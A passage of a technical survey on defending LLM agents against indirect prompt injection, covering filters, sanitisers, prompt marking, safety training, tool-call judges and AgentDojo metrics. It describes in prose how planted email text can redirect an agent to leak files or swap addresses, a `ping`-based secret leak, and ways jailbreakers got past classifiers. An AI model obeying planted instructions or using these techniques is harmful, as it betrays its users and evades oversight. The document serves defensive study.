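# Component-level and system-level defences for LLM agents

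## Where a defence can sit in an LLM agent

An LLM agent is a large language model that works through a task by calling tools in a loop. The tools let it search a mailbox, open files, run commands or move money, and much of what they return is text that strangers wrote. An attacker who plants instructions in that text may get the agent to misuse its tools.

Engineers defend LLM agents in two broad ways. A component-level defence puts a safeguard inside one module: a filter on the model's input, a filter on its output, or extra training for the model. A system-level defence changes the orchestration (the program logic that controls what input each model receives, which tools it may call and in what order) or narrows the agent's permissions, so that a manipulated model can do less harm.

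### One turn of the loop

For example, a user might ask an office assistant with access to their mail and files to "send the March minutes to the address in Bob's latest email".

The agent's program first assembles a prompt containing the developer's standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this process in OpenAI's coding agent Codex. Every item in the initial prompt has a role (system, developer, user or assistant, in decreasing order of priority), which indicates how much weight its content should have. Software then converts the prompt into tokens, which are integers that index into the model's vocabulary. The model produces new tokens that form either a final message to the user or a request for a tool call.

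To search the mailbox, the model emits structured text that names a tool and its arguments, in this case a search for the newest message from Bob. Ordinary code around the model runs the search, appends the full text of Bob's email to the prompt, and queries the model again. The model now has the address and emits a call to fetch the minutes. It then proposes a call to the mail tool with the address and the file as arguments. The code sends the email and appends a confirmation, and the model tells the user that the job is done. A single turn can run to hundreds of tool calls, according to Bolin, and the prompt keeps growing until the program compacts it.

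A tool call proposed by the model is only text until the surrounding code executes it. Whoever writes that code can add a check before execution, and most system-level defences depend on this. But each tool has its own point where a check can go. The sandbox Bolin describes covers the shell tool that Codex provides, while tools from outside servers have to enforce their own guardrails.

### Why instructions and data mix

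By the second pass, the user's request and Bob's email are in the same prompt. A conventional program would receive them through separate interfaces. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) points out that an agent keeps everything in a single context memory, with separators between the parts. The model then processes it all as one sequence.

*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov et al., 2025) traces the problem to how tokens enter the network. A model stores one vector, called an embedding, for each entry in its vocabulary. With V entries and d numbers per vector, the embeddings form a V × d matrix E, and the token with index i always enters as row i of E. The word "send" therefore has the same embedding in the user's request as in Bob's email, and nothing in the vector marks whether it belongs to a command or to material to process. The model learns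 in training to infer the difference from context, but it does so imperfectly. Delimiters and role markers help, but they are only more context.

Databases once had a similar weakness. Programmers pasted user input into queries, so an attacker could type something that the database parsed as a command. Parameterised queries solved this by fixing the structure of the query before the input arrives. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) make this comparison in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*. They explain that the same solution doesn't work for LLMs because natural language lacks a grammar like SQL's, which lets a parser tell code from data. They conclude that something outside the model has to separate instructions from data.

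Training and architecture can still at least improve how well a model separates instructions from data. ASIDE applies a fixed rotation to the embedding of every token that the surrounding program has marked as data, so the model receives different embeddings for "send" in an email and "send" in a request. After ordinary fine-tuning with this change, Zverev and colleagues measured gains of 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points, depending on the model, on a test of whether models execute instructions in the request and ignore those in the data. The success rate of injections fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one benchmark of text tasks, but only from 45% to 36% on another, which is much weaker protection than a parameterised query gives. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, NVIDIA and several universities, conjectures that persistent attackers will always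 get past a separation that depends on the model. The paper supports this with a record of broken defences but does not prove it.

Perfectly separating instructions from data would also make agents less useful. People ask agents to follow the installation steps in a repository or work through a to-do list on a web page, and an agent that ignored all instructions in the data it reads could not do these tasks.

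### Three attacks on one request

Indirect prompt injection means planting instructions in content that an agent reads, such as an email or web page, to make the agent act against its user. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term. Until then, researchers had mostly assumed that the person attacking a model was the person typing to it. In an indirect attack, the user is the victim and the attacker may never interact with the system directly. Microsoft (2025), describing its own defences, notes that a plain text file is enough to carry the instructions, and that attackers can hide them from human readers as white text on a white background.

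Suppose that Bob's latest email forwards a message from an outsider, who wrote the forwarded part with the assistant in mind. The outsider could aim at three different things:

- Attack 1 adds a tool call. The planted text tells the agent to send a salary file to an outside address as well, and the agent does so alongside the real task.
- Attack 2 swaps an argument. The agent makes the call that the user wanted and attaches the right minutes, but the address is the attacker's.
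- Attack 3 changes only what the agent reports. The minutes go to the right place, and the agent then tells the user, falsely, that Bob has cancelled the April meeting.

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) adapts attacks to the defence under test. Its threat model centres on the goals in attacks 1 and 2, where the attacker wants the agent to call a tool the user never asked for, or a legitimate tool with arguments the attacker chose. Attack 3 belongs to what Greshake and colleagues call manipulated content, which includes wrong summaries of documents and emails.

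Attack 2 is harder to defend against because the user told the agent to take the address from the email. Ma and colleagues call such tasks "param-open", meaning that the user specifies the action but leaves a parameter to outside content, as in "pay the bill in this file". The attacker does not need an instruction. A line in the forwarded text such as "please note my new address" could be enough, and a model that ignores every command in an email might still take the wrong address from it. A complete separation of instructions from data, if anyone achieved it, would therefore stop attack 1 but only partly prevent attack 2.

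In attack 3, no tool call deviates from what the user wanted, so a check on tool calls cannot detect the attack. Narisetty and colleagues describe injection in an agent with tools as an authorization problem, not a content problem. This description fits attacks 1 and 2 well but hardly applies to attack 3.

### Where it sits and what decides

Where a defence sits is independent of how it reaches its verdict. Microsoft distinguishes deterministic defences, which can guarantee that a particular attack will fail even when the surrounding system contains a language model, from probabilistic ones, which make an attack less likely to succeed but may miss some instances. In practice, deterministic defences use fixed rules and probabilistic ones use learned models. *Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks* (Ji, Wang and colleagues, 2025) classifies defences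 separately by the stage at which they intervene and by whether their decision process is deterministic or probabilistic. Combining a defence's position with its type of decision process gives four cells.

| | Fixed rules decide | A learned model decides |
|---|---|---|
| Component level | A rule that strips untrusted URLs from the model's output | A classifier that looks for injections in the model's input |
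| System level | A permission check on each proposed tool call | A judge model that reviews each proposed tool call |

The URL-stripping rule blocks a well-known attack in which planted text gets the model to write an image link that points to the attacker's server and contains the user's data in the address. When the user's browser fetches the image, it sends the data to the attacker without the user clicking anything. Removing such links prevents this however the injection is phrased, and Microsoft took deterministic steps of this kind after the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported a vulnerability. The rule would not stop any of the three attacks on the minutes, because none of them uses a link.

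An injection classifier covers a wider range of attacks but misses more of them. Microsoft trained its own, Prompt Shields, on known injection techniques in several languages and keeps updating it. In the example, a classifier would scan Bob's email before the main model reads it. It should catch a blunt version of attack 1, with an order to forward the salary file, but may miss a polite change of address because that looks like ordinary business mail.

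A tool-call judge is a second model that compares the proposed call with the user's request. Sending a salary file has nothing to do with the March minutes, so the judge has good reason to refuse attack 1. In attack 2, the call looks exactly like what the user asked for. To tell the right address from the wrong one, the judge would have to read Bob's email, which would expose it to the attacker's text. Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026), in *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, accept that injected text can manipulate a judge as it can any other model. They still think that some security decisions need a judge, provided that the system shows it only narrow, structured inputs and asks it a narrow question. A judge therefore sits at the system level but can fail as a classifier does.

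In a permission check, code compares the call against a policy that states which actions and data flows the agent is allowed. The policy "Salary files may not leave the company" stops attack 1 every time but not attack 2, because the minutes are not a salary file. A stricter policy that allows attachments to go only to known contacts would also stop attack 2, unless the attacker is a known contact. However, it would block the honest task whenever Bob wants the minutes sent to someone new.

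Enforcing a rule deterministically does not fix gaps in the rule. In one of the real attacks that *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses, a prompt hidden in a code file instructed Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, to read secrets such as API keys and leak them through the network command `ping`. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data out, but its developers had put `ping` on the list of commands that needed no approval. The check therefore allowed `ping`, as its rule specified.

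The second question can also have different answers at different stages of one defence. Progent uses ordinary code to check each tool call against privilege rules, but a language model writes the policy, as Narisetty and colleagues note. In the general architecture of Xiang and colleagues, an orchestrator, usually a model, writes a plan and a policy for the task. An executor then proposes actions, and a policy enforcer, which may be a program or another model, approves or blocks each one. The table above sorts defences by what decides at enforcement, so Progent falls under fixed rules, though a model could introduce a mistake into its policy.

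### Other people's dividing lines

Researchers use different terms for these levels. Xiang and colleagues divide defences into text-level, model-level and system-level. Their text level includes strengthened prompts and monitors that check the wording of inputs and outputs, and their model level includes security training and detectors that read a model's internal activations. Both levels are component-level in the sense used above. Wang and colleagues use text, model and execution levels, and their execution level includes judges that compare a tool call with the user's task. *AgentSys* (2026) divides defences into model-level robustness, detection-based guardrails and system-level control.

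Narisetty and colleagues prefer the terms in-band and out-of-band. An in-band defence works on or inside the model and the channel under attack, while an out-of-band defence enforces a deterministic policy from outside. Each term covers both where a defence sits and how it decides. This suits permission checks and injection classifiers, but a tool-call judge doesn't clearly fit either term because it sits outside the agent's main model and relies on a learned model for its verdict. The paper's comparison table lists one such system, RTBAS, as "mixed".

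Papers also use "system-level" to mean different things. *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States* (2026) uses it only for packages that layer several checks, and lists gates on individual actions separately, as runtime defences. Ma and colleagues sort defences into prompt-level, filter-based and system-level. They count training a model to ignore instructions in the data channel as system-level because it constrains what the agent does instead of screening what it reads. Wang and colleagues classify the same kind of training, such as SecAlign, as model-level. This report treats it as a component-level defence because the safeguard is in the model's weights and the tools and permissions around it don't change.

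Readers who see a claim that system-level defences work well should check which ones the author tested. The broad definition isn't a problem in Ma and colleagues' experiments, because the four system-level defences they tested (Progent, DRIFT, CaMeL and ROPE) all work through plans, permissions or data flow.

### AgentDojo and what it measures

Much of the evidence on these defences comes from one test environment, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). It has four simulated workplaces, each with its own tools, ordinary user tasks and attacker goals. The security cases pair every user task with every attacker goal in the same workplace.

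| Environment | Tools | User tasks | Attacker goals | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |
| Total | 74 | 97 | 27 | 629 |

The agent runs its full loop, and its calls change the state of the environment. For example, an email it sends appears in the simulated outbox. Some items in the environment, such as message bodies, have placeholders for the attacker's text. Each user task comes with a correct sequence of tool calls, which lets the experimenters place injections in items the agent will have to read. When the run ends, ordinary code checks the state, and the agent's answer where necessary, to decide whether the user's task succeeded and whether the attacker's goal was achieved. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided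 using a language model as the grader because a strong injection might hijack it too.

Attack success rate is the share of attack attempts that achieve the attacker's goal. Clean utility, which AgentDojo calls benign utility, is the share of ordinary tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which the agent completes the user's task without harmful side effects while the injection is present.

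The attacks on the minutes show why one number is not enough to evaluate a defence. If attack 1 works, the agent may send both the salary file and the minutes. The attacker succeeds, and the finished task does not count towards AgentDojo's utility under attack because of the side effect. Ma and colleagues define utility under attack as task completion with the injection present, which on that wording would count the task, so figures under this name may not be comparable between papers. If a filter detects the injection and aborts the run, both the attacker and the user fail. An agent that refused every request would have zero attack success rate and zero clean utility. The attack success rate largely misses attack 3, since AgentDojo defines success as the agent carrying out malicious actions. Attack 3 might lower measured utility if the check for that task reads the agent's answer.

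Small details of an attack can considerably change how often it succeeds. Against GPT-4o in 2024, an injection that addressed the model and the user by their correct names succeeded in 47.7% of cases, compared with about 23% when either name was wrong. The attacker's goal also matters. One goal in AgentDojo's travel suite required the agent to book the most expensive hotel in Paris and email out the user's personal information. This attack never succeeded, often because the agent did only one of the two tasks and both were required for success.

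Debenedetti and colleagues intended other researchers to add new attacks to AgentDojo, and warned that it is easy to build a defence that stops any particular attack. Most later evaluations have nevertheless used static attacks, which researchers fix in advance without regard to the defence under test. An adaptive attack changes in response to the defence. A static attack's low success rate may not be due to the defence. Ma and colleagues found that AgentDojo's standard injection succeeded 0.3% of the time on Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defence installed.

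Xiang and colleagues note that only 6 of the 97 user tasks require the agent to revise its plan or policy along the way. A defence that fixes the plan at the start, or cuts the agent off from most of what it reads, therefore loses little utility on these tasks. It could lose far more in an office where Bob's email changes what the agent needs to do next.

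## Filters on what the model reads and writes

A filter blocks or cleans text on its way into or out of the model. The agent can still read Bob's email, revise its plan and call any of its tools, so developers can add a filter without redesigning the agent. Input and output filters are the most widely deployed defences, according to *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026). But a filter has to recognise an attack almost entirely from its text.

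### How a classifier scores a passage

The cheapest learned filters are encoder classifiers. An encoder is a language model that turns a passage into vectors and writes no text of its own. Meta's Prompt Guard and the academic model PIGuard both build on a family of encoders called DeBERTa. In its simplest form, such a classifier works in four steps:

1. Software splits the passage into tokens and puts a marker token in front.
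2. The encoder gives each token a vector. Its layers then mix information between the vectors, so the vector for "ignore" comes to reflect the words on both sides of it, and the marker's vector comes to reflect the whole passage.
3. A final layer multiplies the marker's vector h by learned weights w and adds a constant b. The result, z = w · h + b, can be any number, and the function p = 1 / (1 + e^(−z)) converts it into a score between 0 and 1.
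4. Ordinary code compares p with a threshold t. If p is at least t, the program treats the passage as an attack.

Training sets the weights from labelled examples, but a person chooses the threshold t. Lowering t catches more attacks but also raises more false alarms, so a detection rate means little without the false-alarm rate at the same threshold.

Meta's model card for *Llama Prompt Guard 2 22M* reports detection rates at the threshold where the filter flags 1% of harmless inputs. The first Prompt Guard detected only 21.2% of attacks. In the second version, the model with 86 million parameters detects 97.5% and takes 92 milliseconds per input, while the model with 22 million detects 88.7% and takes 19 milliseconds. Meta attributes the improvement to a new training objective that gives the highest scores to prompts resembling known attacks, even on unfamiliar kinds of data. According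 to Groq, which hosts the larger model, these figures measure the detection of English jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to make a model break its safety rules. The figures are therefore little direct evidence of how well the filter detects instructions hidden in an email.

Groq reports that in Meta's tests on AgentDojo, the larger model had an attack prevention rate of 81.2% "with minimal utility impact". Learnopoly's *META AI OPEN-SOURCE LLAMAFIREWALL*, a summary of Meta's results, reports a smaller reduction of 57%, with the model cutting the attack success rate from 17.6% to 7.5%. The figures may differ because of different thresholds or attacks.

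Prompt Guard 2 and PIGuard accept at most 512 tokens at a time, which is a few hundred English words, so the agent's program has to split a longer email into pieces and score each one. Each piece adds another chance of a false alarm, and an instruction split between two pieces could look harmless in each.

### Trigger words

Classifiers can learn to react to certain words instead of recognising injections. In *InjecGuard*, Li and Liu (2024) gave a popular classifier from ProtectAI a harmless question about whether one can ignore a warning in some code. The classifier put most of its attention on the word "ignore" and labelled the question an injection.

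Li and Liu built a test set called NotInject to measure this tendency. They looked for words that rank much higher by frequency in attack data than in ordinary prompts, then had a language model and three human reviewers remove irrelevant ones. GPT-4o-mini then wrote 339 harmless sentences, each containing one, two or three of the remaining words. Li and Liu took their attacks and ordinary harmless text from existing public benchmarks.

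| Filter | Attacks caught | Ordinary harmless text passed | NotInject sentences passed | Time per input |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Guard, first version | 97.1% | 26.8% | 0.9% | 15 ms |
| ProtectAI v2 | 48.6% | 86.2% | 56.6% | 16 ms |
| Llama Guard 3 | 28.3% | 95.2% | 99.7% | 787 ms |
| GPT-4o with a detection prompt | 79.1% | 90.8% | 86.7% | 7,907 ms |
| PIGuard | 77.4% | 85.7% | 87.3% | 15 ms |

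PIGuard, first released as InjecGuard, is Li and Liu's own classifier. They trained it on about 61,000 harmless texts and 15,700 injections, then fed it every token in its vocabulary, one at a time. A single token can't be an attack, so any token that set off the classifier exposed a bias. Li and Liu had GPT-4o-mini write 1,000 harmless texts around these tokens, added them to the training data, and retrained the classifier from scratch. The share of NotInject sentences it let through rose from 64.3% to 87.3%, and it also caught slightly more attacks.

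That result probably slightly overstates PIGuard's performance, because the extra training texts and the test sentences were produced in much the same way. PIGuard flagged about 14% of the ordinary harmless text and missed 23% of the attacks. It is far better balanced than the first Prompt Guard, which flagged almost everything, but an office assistant that lost one harmless email in seven would be hard to use.

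### Finding and removing injected text

A filter that detects an injection can reject the whole document or try to clean it. Shi, Zhu and colleagues (2025), in *PromptArmor*, built a sanitiser, a filter that removes the suspicious part, from an ordinary language model with no extra training. It processes each tool result before the agent's main model reads it:

1. The program sends the tool result to a guardrail model and asks whether it contains an injected prompt. The guardrail model can use the user's task as context and look for text that diverges from it.
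2. If the answer is yes, the guardrail model copies out the injected text.
3. Models often change spaces or punctuation when they copy, so code takes only the words from the copy and builds a search pattern that allows any characters between them.
4. Code deletes the matching passage and gives the rest to the agent.

Shi and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo's 629 security cases with an agent running on GPT-4.1. They used four standard attack wordings, such as one that tells the model to ignore its previous instructions, and counted an attacker's goal as achieved if any of the four worked. The table gives false alarms as a share of clean tool results and misses as a share of contaminated ones.

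| Filter | False alarms | Misses | Attack success rate | Utility under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | – | 54.5% | 64.3% |
| PromptArmor with GPT-4.1 | 0.56% | 0.13% | 0.0% | 72.0% |
| PromptArmor with GPT-4o | 0.07% | 0.23% | 0.5% | 68.7% |
| PromptArmor with GPT-3.5 | 11.24% | 15.74% | 6.8% | 51.4% |
| ProtectAI's DeBERTa classifier | 28.41% | 22.03% | 18.9% | 29.7% |
| DataSentinel | 0.10% | 48.78% | 38.6% | 46.4% |

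Utility under attack rises with the newer models because the agent can finish the user's task once the injection is gone. GPT-4.1 is also good at detecting attacks that often work on it. A model that follows an injected instruction in the middle of a task can still recognise that instruction when it is only asked to detect injections.

The guardrail model has to be capable enough to tell contaminated tool results from clean ones. GPT-3.5 had not learned what "prompt injection" meant, and missed 60% of contaminated results until Shi and colleagues added a definition to its prompt. The smallest model they tried, Qwen3 with 0.6 billion parameters, wrongly flagged 63% of clean results. When it reasoned first, it missed 76% of contaminated ones. The 32-billion-parameter version had error rates close to zero on both clean and contaminated results, but it takes much more compute to run on every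 tool result than an encoder does.

DataSentinel, in the last row, instructs a language model, the detector, to repeat a secret key while processing the document. An injection should divert the detector from this task so that it fails to output the key, and the developers trained it to be easy to divert. DataSentinel rarely raises a false alarm, but in this test it missed almost half of the contaminated results. *SpanGuard* (2026) lists other recent sanitisers, including PromptLocate, which locates the injected instructions within a document, and DataFilter, a trained model that takes the user's request into account when removing malicious instructions.

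PromptArmor's near-perfect results are for attacks with a recognisable style. Shi and colleagues also tested it against an automated attacker that revised its wording, which had little success. However, *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports that adaptive attacks often bypass detectors that rely on a model.

### Replies, code and links

An output filter inspects what the model has written before it reaches a user, a browser or an interpreter. It can catch some attacks that looked harmless in the input. Kim and colleagues note that output filters usually take longer than input filters, because they depend on the model's output and have more text to process.

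Filters on replies are usually classifiers that sort text into categories of harmful content. Red Hat (2026) put two filters around an IT support agent, Prompt Guard to detect attacks and Meta's Llama Guard to check content. The filters blocked normal work such as looking up an employee or giving technical support, so the team had to switch off some content categories.

*LlamaFirewall* (2025) presents Meta's open-source package of guardrails for agents, which includes Prompt Guard 2 and a code filter, CodeShield. The filter scans generated code for common flaws, such as SQL injection vulnerabilities, before anyone runs it. Learnopoly reports that, on a labelled set of code samples, 96% of CodeShield's warnings were correct and it found 79% of the insecure samples.

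Malicious code isn't necessarily insecure, however. A correctly written script that uploads the salary file to an outside server may contain no flaw. *On Understanding, Identifying, and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in Agentic Large Language Models* (2026) makes the general point that output filters reduce the risk of executing bad code but don't account for harm in what valid code does.

Link filters, such as the rule that stops the image-link attack, are simpler. Code checks the domain of each web address in the output against a list of permitted domains and deletes the address if its domain is not listed. Kim and colleagues describe the same idea for inputs, with an allowlist of sites from which an agent may retrieve data. Neither rule helps when the attacker can write to a permitted source, such as a mailbox, which can receive messages from anyone who knows the email address.

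Filters that check only a single session also miss harm that happens later. If planted text gets the agent to save a false note in its long-term memory, that session's output may look harmless, and the agent could act on the note a week later.

### Marking the prompt and training the model

Other component-level defences try to make the main model less likely to obey instructions in untrusted text. The simplest of these defences change the prompt. *Defending Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks With Spotlighting* (2024) describes several ways to mark untrusted text. Delimiting puts symbols around a document and tells the model never to obey instructions between them. Datamarking repeats a special token throughout the document, so that every part of it is marked.

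Google used a version of datamarking in its tests of Gemini. It inserted a control token after every eight characters of an email's sender, subject and body, and added a warning to the system instruction. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that this worked mainly by breaking up the tokens of phrases that trigger an injection. The effect therefore depends on how text splits into tokens, and Google expected it to be weaker in some languages.

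Marking adds almost no overhead, but plain delimiters do little to stop attacks. In Shi and colleagues' test, delimiters reduced the attack success rate only from 54.5% to 51.5%, while repeating the user's request reduced it to 29.9%.

The alternative is to train the model to ignore instructions in data. *StruQ* (2024) uses a front end to put the instruction and the data into separate parts of a fixed format, and fine-tunes the model on examples that have injections in the data part and correct answers that follow only the real instruction. *SecAlign* (2024) gives the model pairs of answers to the same contaminated input and trains it to prefer the answer that follows the user over the one that follows the attacker. Both methods stopped simple handwritten injections in their developers' tests. Attack strings optimised by an algorithm succeeded less than a quarter as often against SecAlign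 as against StruQ.

*A Critical Evaluation of Defenses against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2025) points out that these success rates came mainly from tests with one injected prompt, "Print exactly Hacked!", and reports markedly different results from its own tests with optimised attacks. Shi and colleagues left SecAlign out of their comparison because it performed poorly on AgentDojo's ordinary tasks even without an attack. They attribute this to a loss of general instruction-following ability, which an agent needs more than a chatbot does.

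### When nearly every document is clean

Attacks usually make up a much larger share of the documents in a filter test than in a real mailbox. Suppose that 1 document in 10,000 contains an injection, and that a filter catches 99% of injections and raises a false alarm on 1% of clean documents. In a million documents, the filter would catch 99 of the 100 malicious ones and flag 9,999 of the 999,900 clean ones. Only about 1% of its 10,098 alarms would be real.

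In general, if π is the share of malicious documents, d the detection rate and f the false-alarm rate, the chance that an alarm is real is

πd / (πd + (1 − π)f).

Catching more injections hardly changes this. Even if the filter caught every injection, only 100 of 10,099 alarms would be real. Lowering the false-alarm rate f helps much more, but f would have to fall to about 1 in 10,000 for half of the alarms to be real. PromptArmor with GPT-4o had a false-alarm rate of 0.07% on AgentDojo. If it kept that rate on real documents, about one alarm in eight would be real.

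The rate of 1 in 10,000 is an illustration, and the true rate will vary between mailboxes. The rate also affects how to read a classifier's score. About a fifth of PIGuard's training examples were injections. If its scores were accurate probabilities for that mixture, a document scoring 0.9 would have only about a 0.35% chance of being malicious in a mailbox where 1 document in 10,000 is malicious.

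Agents also read many documents per task. If a filter has a 1% false-alarm rate per document and its errors are independent, the chance of at least one false alarm across 50 clean documents is 1 − 0.99^50, or about 39%.

False alarms may well be correlated. If a company's newsletter template always triggers the filter, the alarms will cluster in tasks that involve newsletters, and fewer tasks will have one. In the extreme case where all of a task's documents trigger the filter or none do, only 1% of tasks would be affected. The 39% also depends on the false-alarm rate. At PromptArmor's rates with GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, it would be about 3% and 24%. At the 28% rate that Shi and colleagues measured for ProtectAI's classifier, 81% of tasks with just five clean documents would have a false alarm.

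How much false alarms matter depends on what the system does after an alarm. A filter that aborts the run turns every false alarm into a failed task. In the first example, a filter that asks a person to check would send them about 100 clean documents for each malicious one, and they might soon stop looking carefully. A sanitiser lets the run continue, but it could delete the line containing the address Bob wants the agent to use. The least disruptive response is to send the suspicious document to a slower and more accurate filter.

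### What a second filter adds

Suppose that two filters each miss 10% of attacks and that either can block a document. It is tempting to multiply the rates and conclude that only 1% of attacks get past both. The correct formula is

P(both miss) = P(A misses) × P(B misses, given that A missed).

The second factor is 10% only if the filters' errors are independent. If B misses half of the attacks that A missed, 5% of all attacks get through. If B misses exactly the attacks that A misses, 10% still get through.

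Different filters can miss the same attacks for several reasons. Developers often train them on the same public collections of attacks. They also tend to use small models for speed, and Red Hat's *Beyond guardrails* (2026) warns that attackers can hide an injection in a puzzle or role-play that a small model can't decode but the agent's main model can. A filter as capable as the main model would close this gap, but it would make the agent slower and more expensive. Some attacks, such as a politely worded change of address, contain nothing suspicious for any filter to detect.

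Meta's AgentDojo results give a rough idea of how far off the multiplication is in practice. Prompt Guard 2 alone reduced attack success from 17.6% to 7.5%. AlignmentCheck, a model that checks whether the agent is still pursuing the user's goal, reduced it to 2.9% on its own. If the two had failed independently, attacks would have succeeded 17.6% × (7.5/17.6) × (2.9/17.6) = 1.2% of the time with both in place. The measured figure was 1.75%, so adding the second defence clearly helped, though less than independence would predict. Two injection classifiers would probably miss more of the same attacks, because these two defences work in quite different ways.

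Adding filters also increases false alarms. If either of two filters can block a document and each wrongly flags 1% of clean ones, together they would flag almost 2%, assuming their errors are independent. An agent that reads 50 clean documents per task would then encounter at least one false alarm in 63% of tasks, compared with 39% with one filter. Filters can also interfere with each other. Kim and colleagues give the example of a sanitiser that removes safety instructions a later guardrail relies on.

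### The case for filters

Filters are still worth using despite these problems. An encoder adds milliseconds to a loop in which each model call may take seconds. Most filters can be added without changing the agent's structure, prompts or main model, as can about half of the 41 defences that Wang and colleagues reviewed. Filters also stop known attacks, which anyone can copy. Red Hat compares them to web application firewalls, which provide a safety net against known attacks but do not replace a secure application.

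Filters can also address harms that consist of text, such as an explanation of how to make a weapon. Permission rules cannot prevent these harms, because the model needs no tool to write text. The strongest evidence for filters comes from work on such harms.

*Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) describes two filters that Anthropic trained to block jailbreaks, one for the user's prompts and one for the model's replies. Anthropic wrote a "constitution", a list of permitted and forbidden kinds of content, and used it to generate training examples. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reports that the original system required 23% more computation and refused 0.38% of real traffic. Attackers had also found ways around it. Some scattered a forbidden question across the functions of a computer program and asked the model to reassemble it. Others had the model answer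 in code words, such as calling chemicals "food flavorings". The output filter could not interpret these replies because it did not have the prompt that explained the code.

The new system examines the prompt and the reply together, in two stages:

1. While the main model (Claude Sonnet 4.5) writes, a linear probe scores each token. The probe is a weighted sum of the activations that the model has already computed, so it costs almost nothing to run. Averaging over neighbouring tokens prevents a single odd word from causing an alarm.
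2. If the score passes a threshold, which happened for about 5.5% of traffic, the system sends the exchange to a separate classifier fine-tuned from Claude Haiku 4.5. The final score is z = 0.55 × z_probe + 0.45 × z_classifier.

An alarm in the first stage only triggers a second check, so the probe can be sensitive without causing many refusals. This is a practical answer to the base-rate problem. The combination also works because the two parts make different mistakes. On about 7,000 exchanges with human attackers, the probe's scores were less correlated with those of the Haiku classifier than the scores of two separate classifiers were with each other. Adding the probe reduced successful attacks more than adding a second classifier did, although all were trained on similar data. Cunningham and colleagues chose the weights for this comparison on the test set, but found that equal weights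 did nearly as well.

In a month of real traffic, the system flagged 0.05% of queries and used 3.5% of the computing power that the previous generation's filters needed. Anthropic then paid people to try to get past the system and obtain answers to eight questions about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. They found one serious vulnerability in roughly 1,700 hours and 198,000 attempts. A vulnerability counted as serious if the attack got answers to more than five of the questions, with at least half the detail an unprotected model would give. Nobody got answers to all eight questions. The previous generation had 13 serious vulnerabilities in 695,000 attempts.

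One vulnerability is too few to estimate a rate precisely, and the advantage over the intermediate versions, which had two and five, could be due to chance. Experts outside the paid programme also completely broke one of those versions, using automated tools and a lot of effort. Still, these attackers could adapt to the defence, so these results are much better evidence than a test on fixed attacks.

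We shouldn't expect a classifier to perform as well against injections. It can learn to recognise detailed instructions for a nerve agent because that content is dangerous whoever asks for it, but an injection is wrong because of who wrote it. The same words, such as "Send the minutes to this address", can be a legitimate request from the user or an attack from a stranger.

A jailbreaker also needs a long, accurate answer, and the model becomes less competent when it has to disguise that answer from a filter. Claude Opus 4's score on a set of difficult science questions fell from 74.2% to 49% with one disguise and to 32.3% with another. An attacker who wants an agent to use the wrong email address needs only a few characters of output and doesn't have to disguise them.

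### Filters against the three attacks

A sanitiser can remove a blunt version of attack 1 as well as flag it. PromptArmor should detect that the order to send the salary file is unrelated to the March minutes and remove the order, and the agent would then send the minutes as normal. The attacker's best chance is to make the order look like routine correspondence, for example by adding that the auditors always receive the salary file together with the minutes.

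Filters are much weaker against attack 2, which needs no command. The text supplies exactly what the user asked for, so even a capable guardrail model that is given the user's request would need outside information, such as Bob's entry in the company directory, to tell the two addresses apart. An output filter has the same difficulty, since the finished email has the right attachment and a normal-looking recipient.

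The closest experimental evidence comes from Wang and colleagues, who built the AgentPI benchmark for tasks in which the agent has to rely on what it reads. In one type of attack, planted text changes a value, such as an account number or filename, that the agent must copy into a tool call. They tested delimiters, paraphrasing and two kinds of added instructions on an agent running on GPT-4o-mini, and none did significantly better than no defence. They did not test encoder classifiers or PromptArmor, so the result supports the argument only indirectly.

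Filters can miss Attack 3, the false report about the April meeting, even though the harm consists of text. An input filter has a fair chance of catching the attack if the planted text orders the agent to make the report. But the outsider could instead write "Bob has cancelled the April meeting" in the forwarded message. That sentence is not malicious in itself, and the agent's reply would accurately summarise the email. A content classifier would pass the reply because the only thing wrong with it is that it is false.

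## Models that judge proposed tool calls

A tool-call judge compares what the agent proposes to do with what the user asked for, so it depends less than a filter does on how the attacker words the injection. Existing judges differ in how much of the attacker's text they read.

### Does the call serve the user's goal?

Task Shield puts this question to a model directly. Jia, Qin and colleagues (2024), in *The Task Shield*, argue that a defence shouldn't ask whether an instruction is harmful, because injected instructions often look harmless. It should ask whether the instruction serves the user's task. Their system works as follows:

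1. A model extracts the tasks from the user's messages and stores them in a list.
2. The model also extracts every instruction from later messages, including tool results and the agent's own proposed calls.
3. It scores how much each instruction i contributes to each user task j, with a number c_ij between 0 and 1.
4. Code adds up the scores for each instruction, C_i = Σ_j c_ij, and flags the instruction if the total is zero.
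5. A flagged tool call doesn't run. The agent receives a warning and a reminder of the user's tasks, and can try again.

The scores are graded because many useful steps don't complete a task by themselves. Checking which rooms are free, for example, contributes a lot to booking one. But the check flags a call only if its scores total zero, so a call with any plausible connection to the task can pass.

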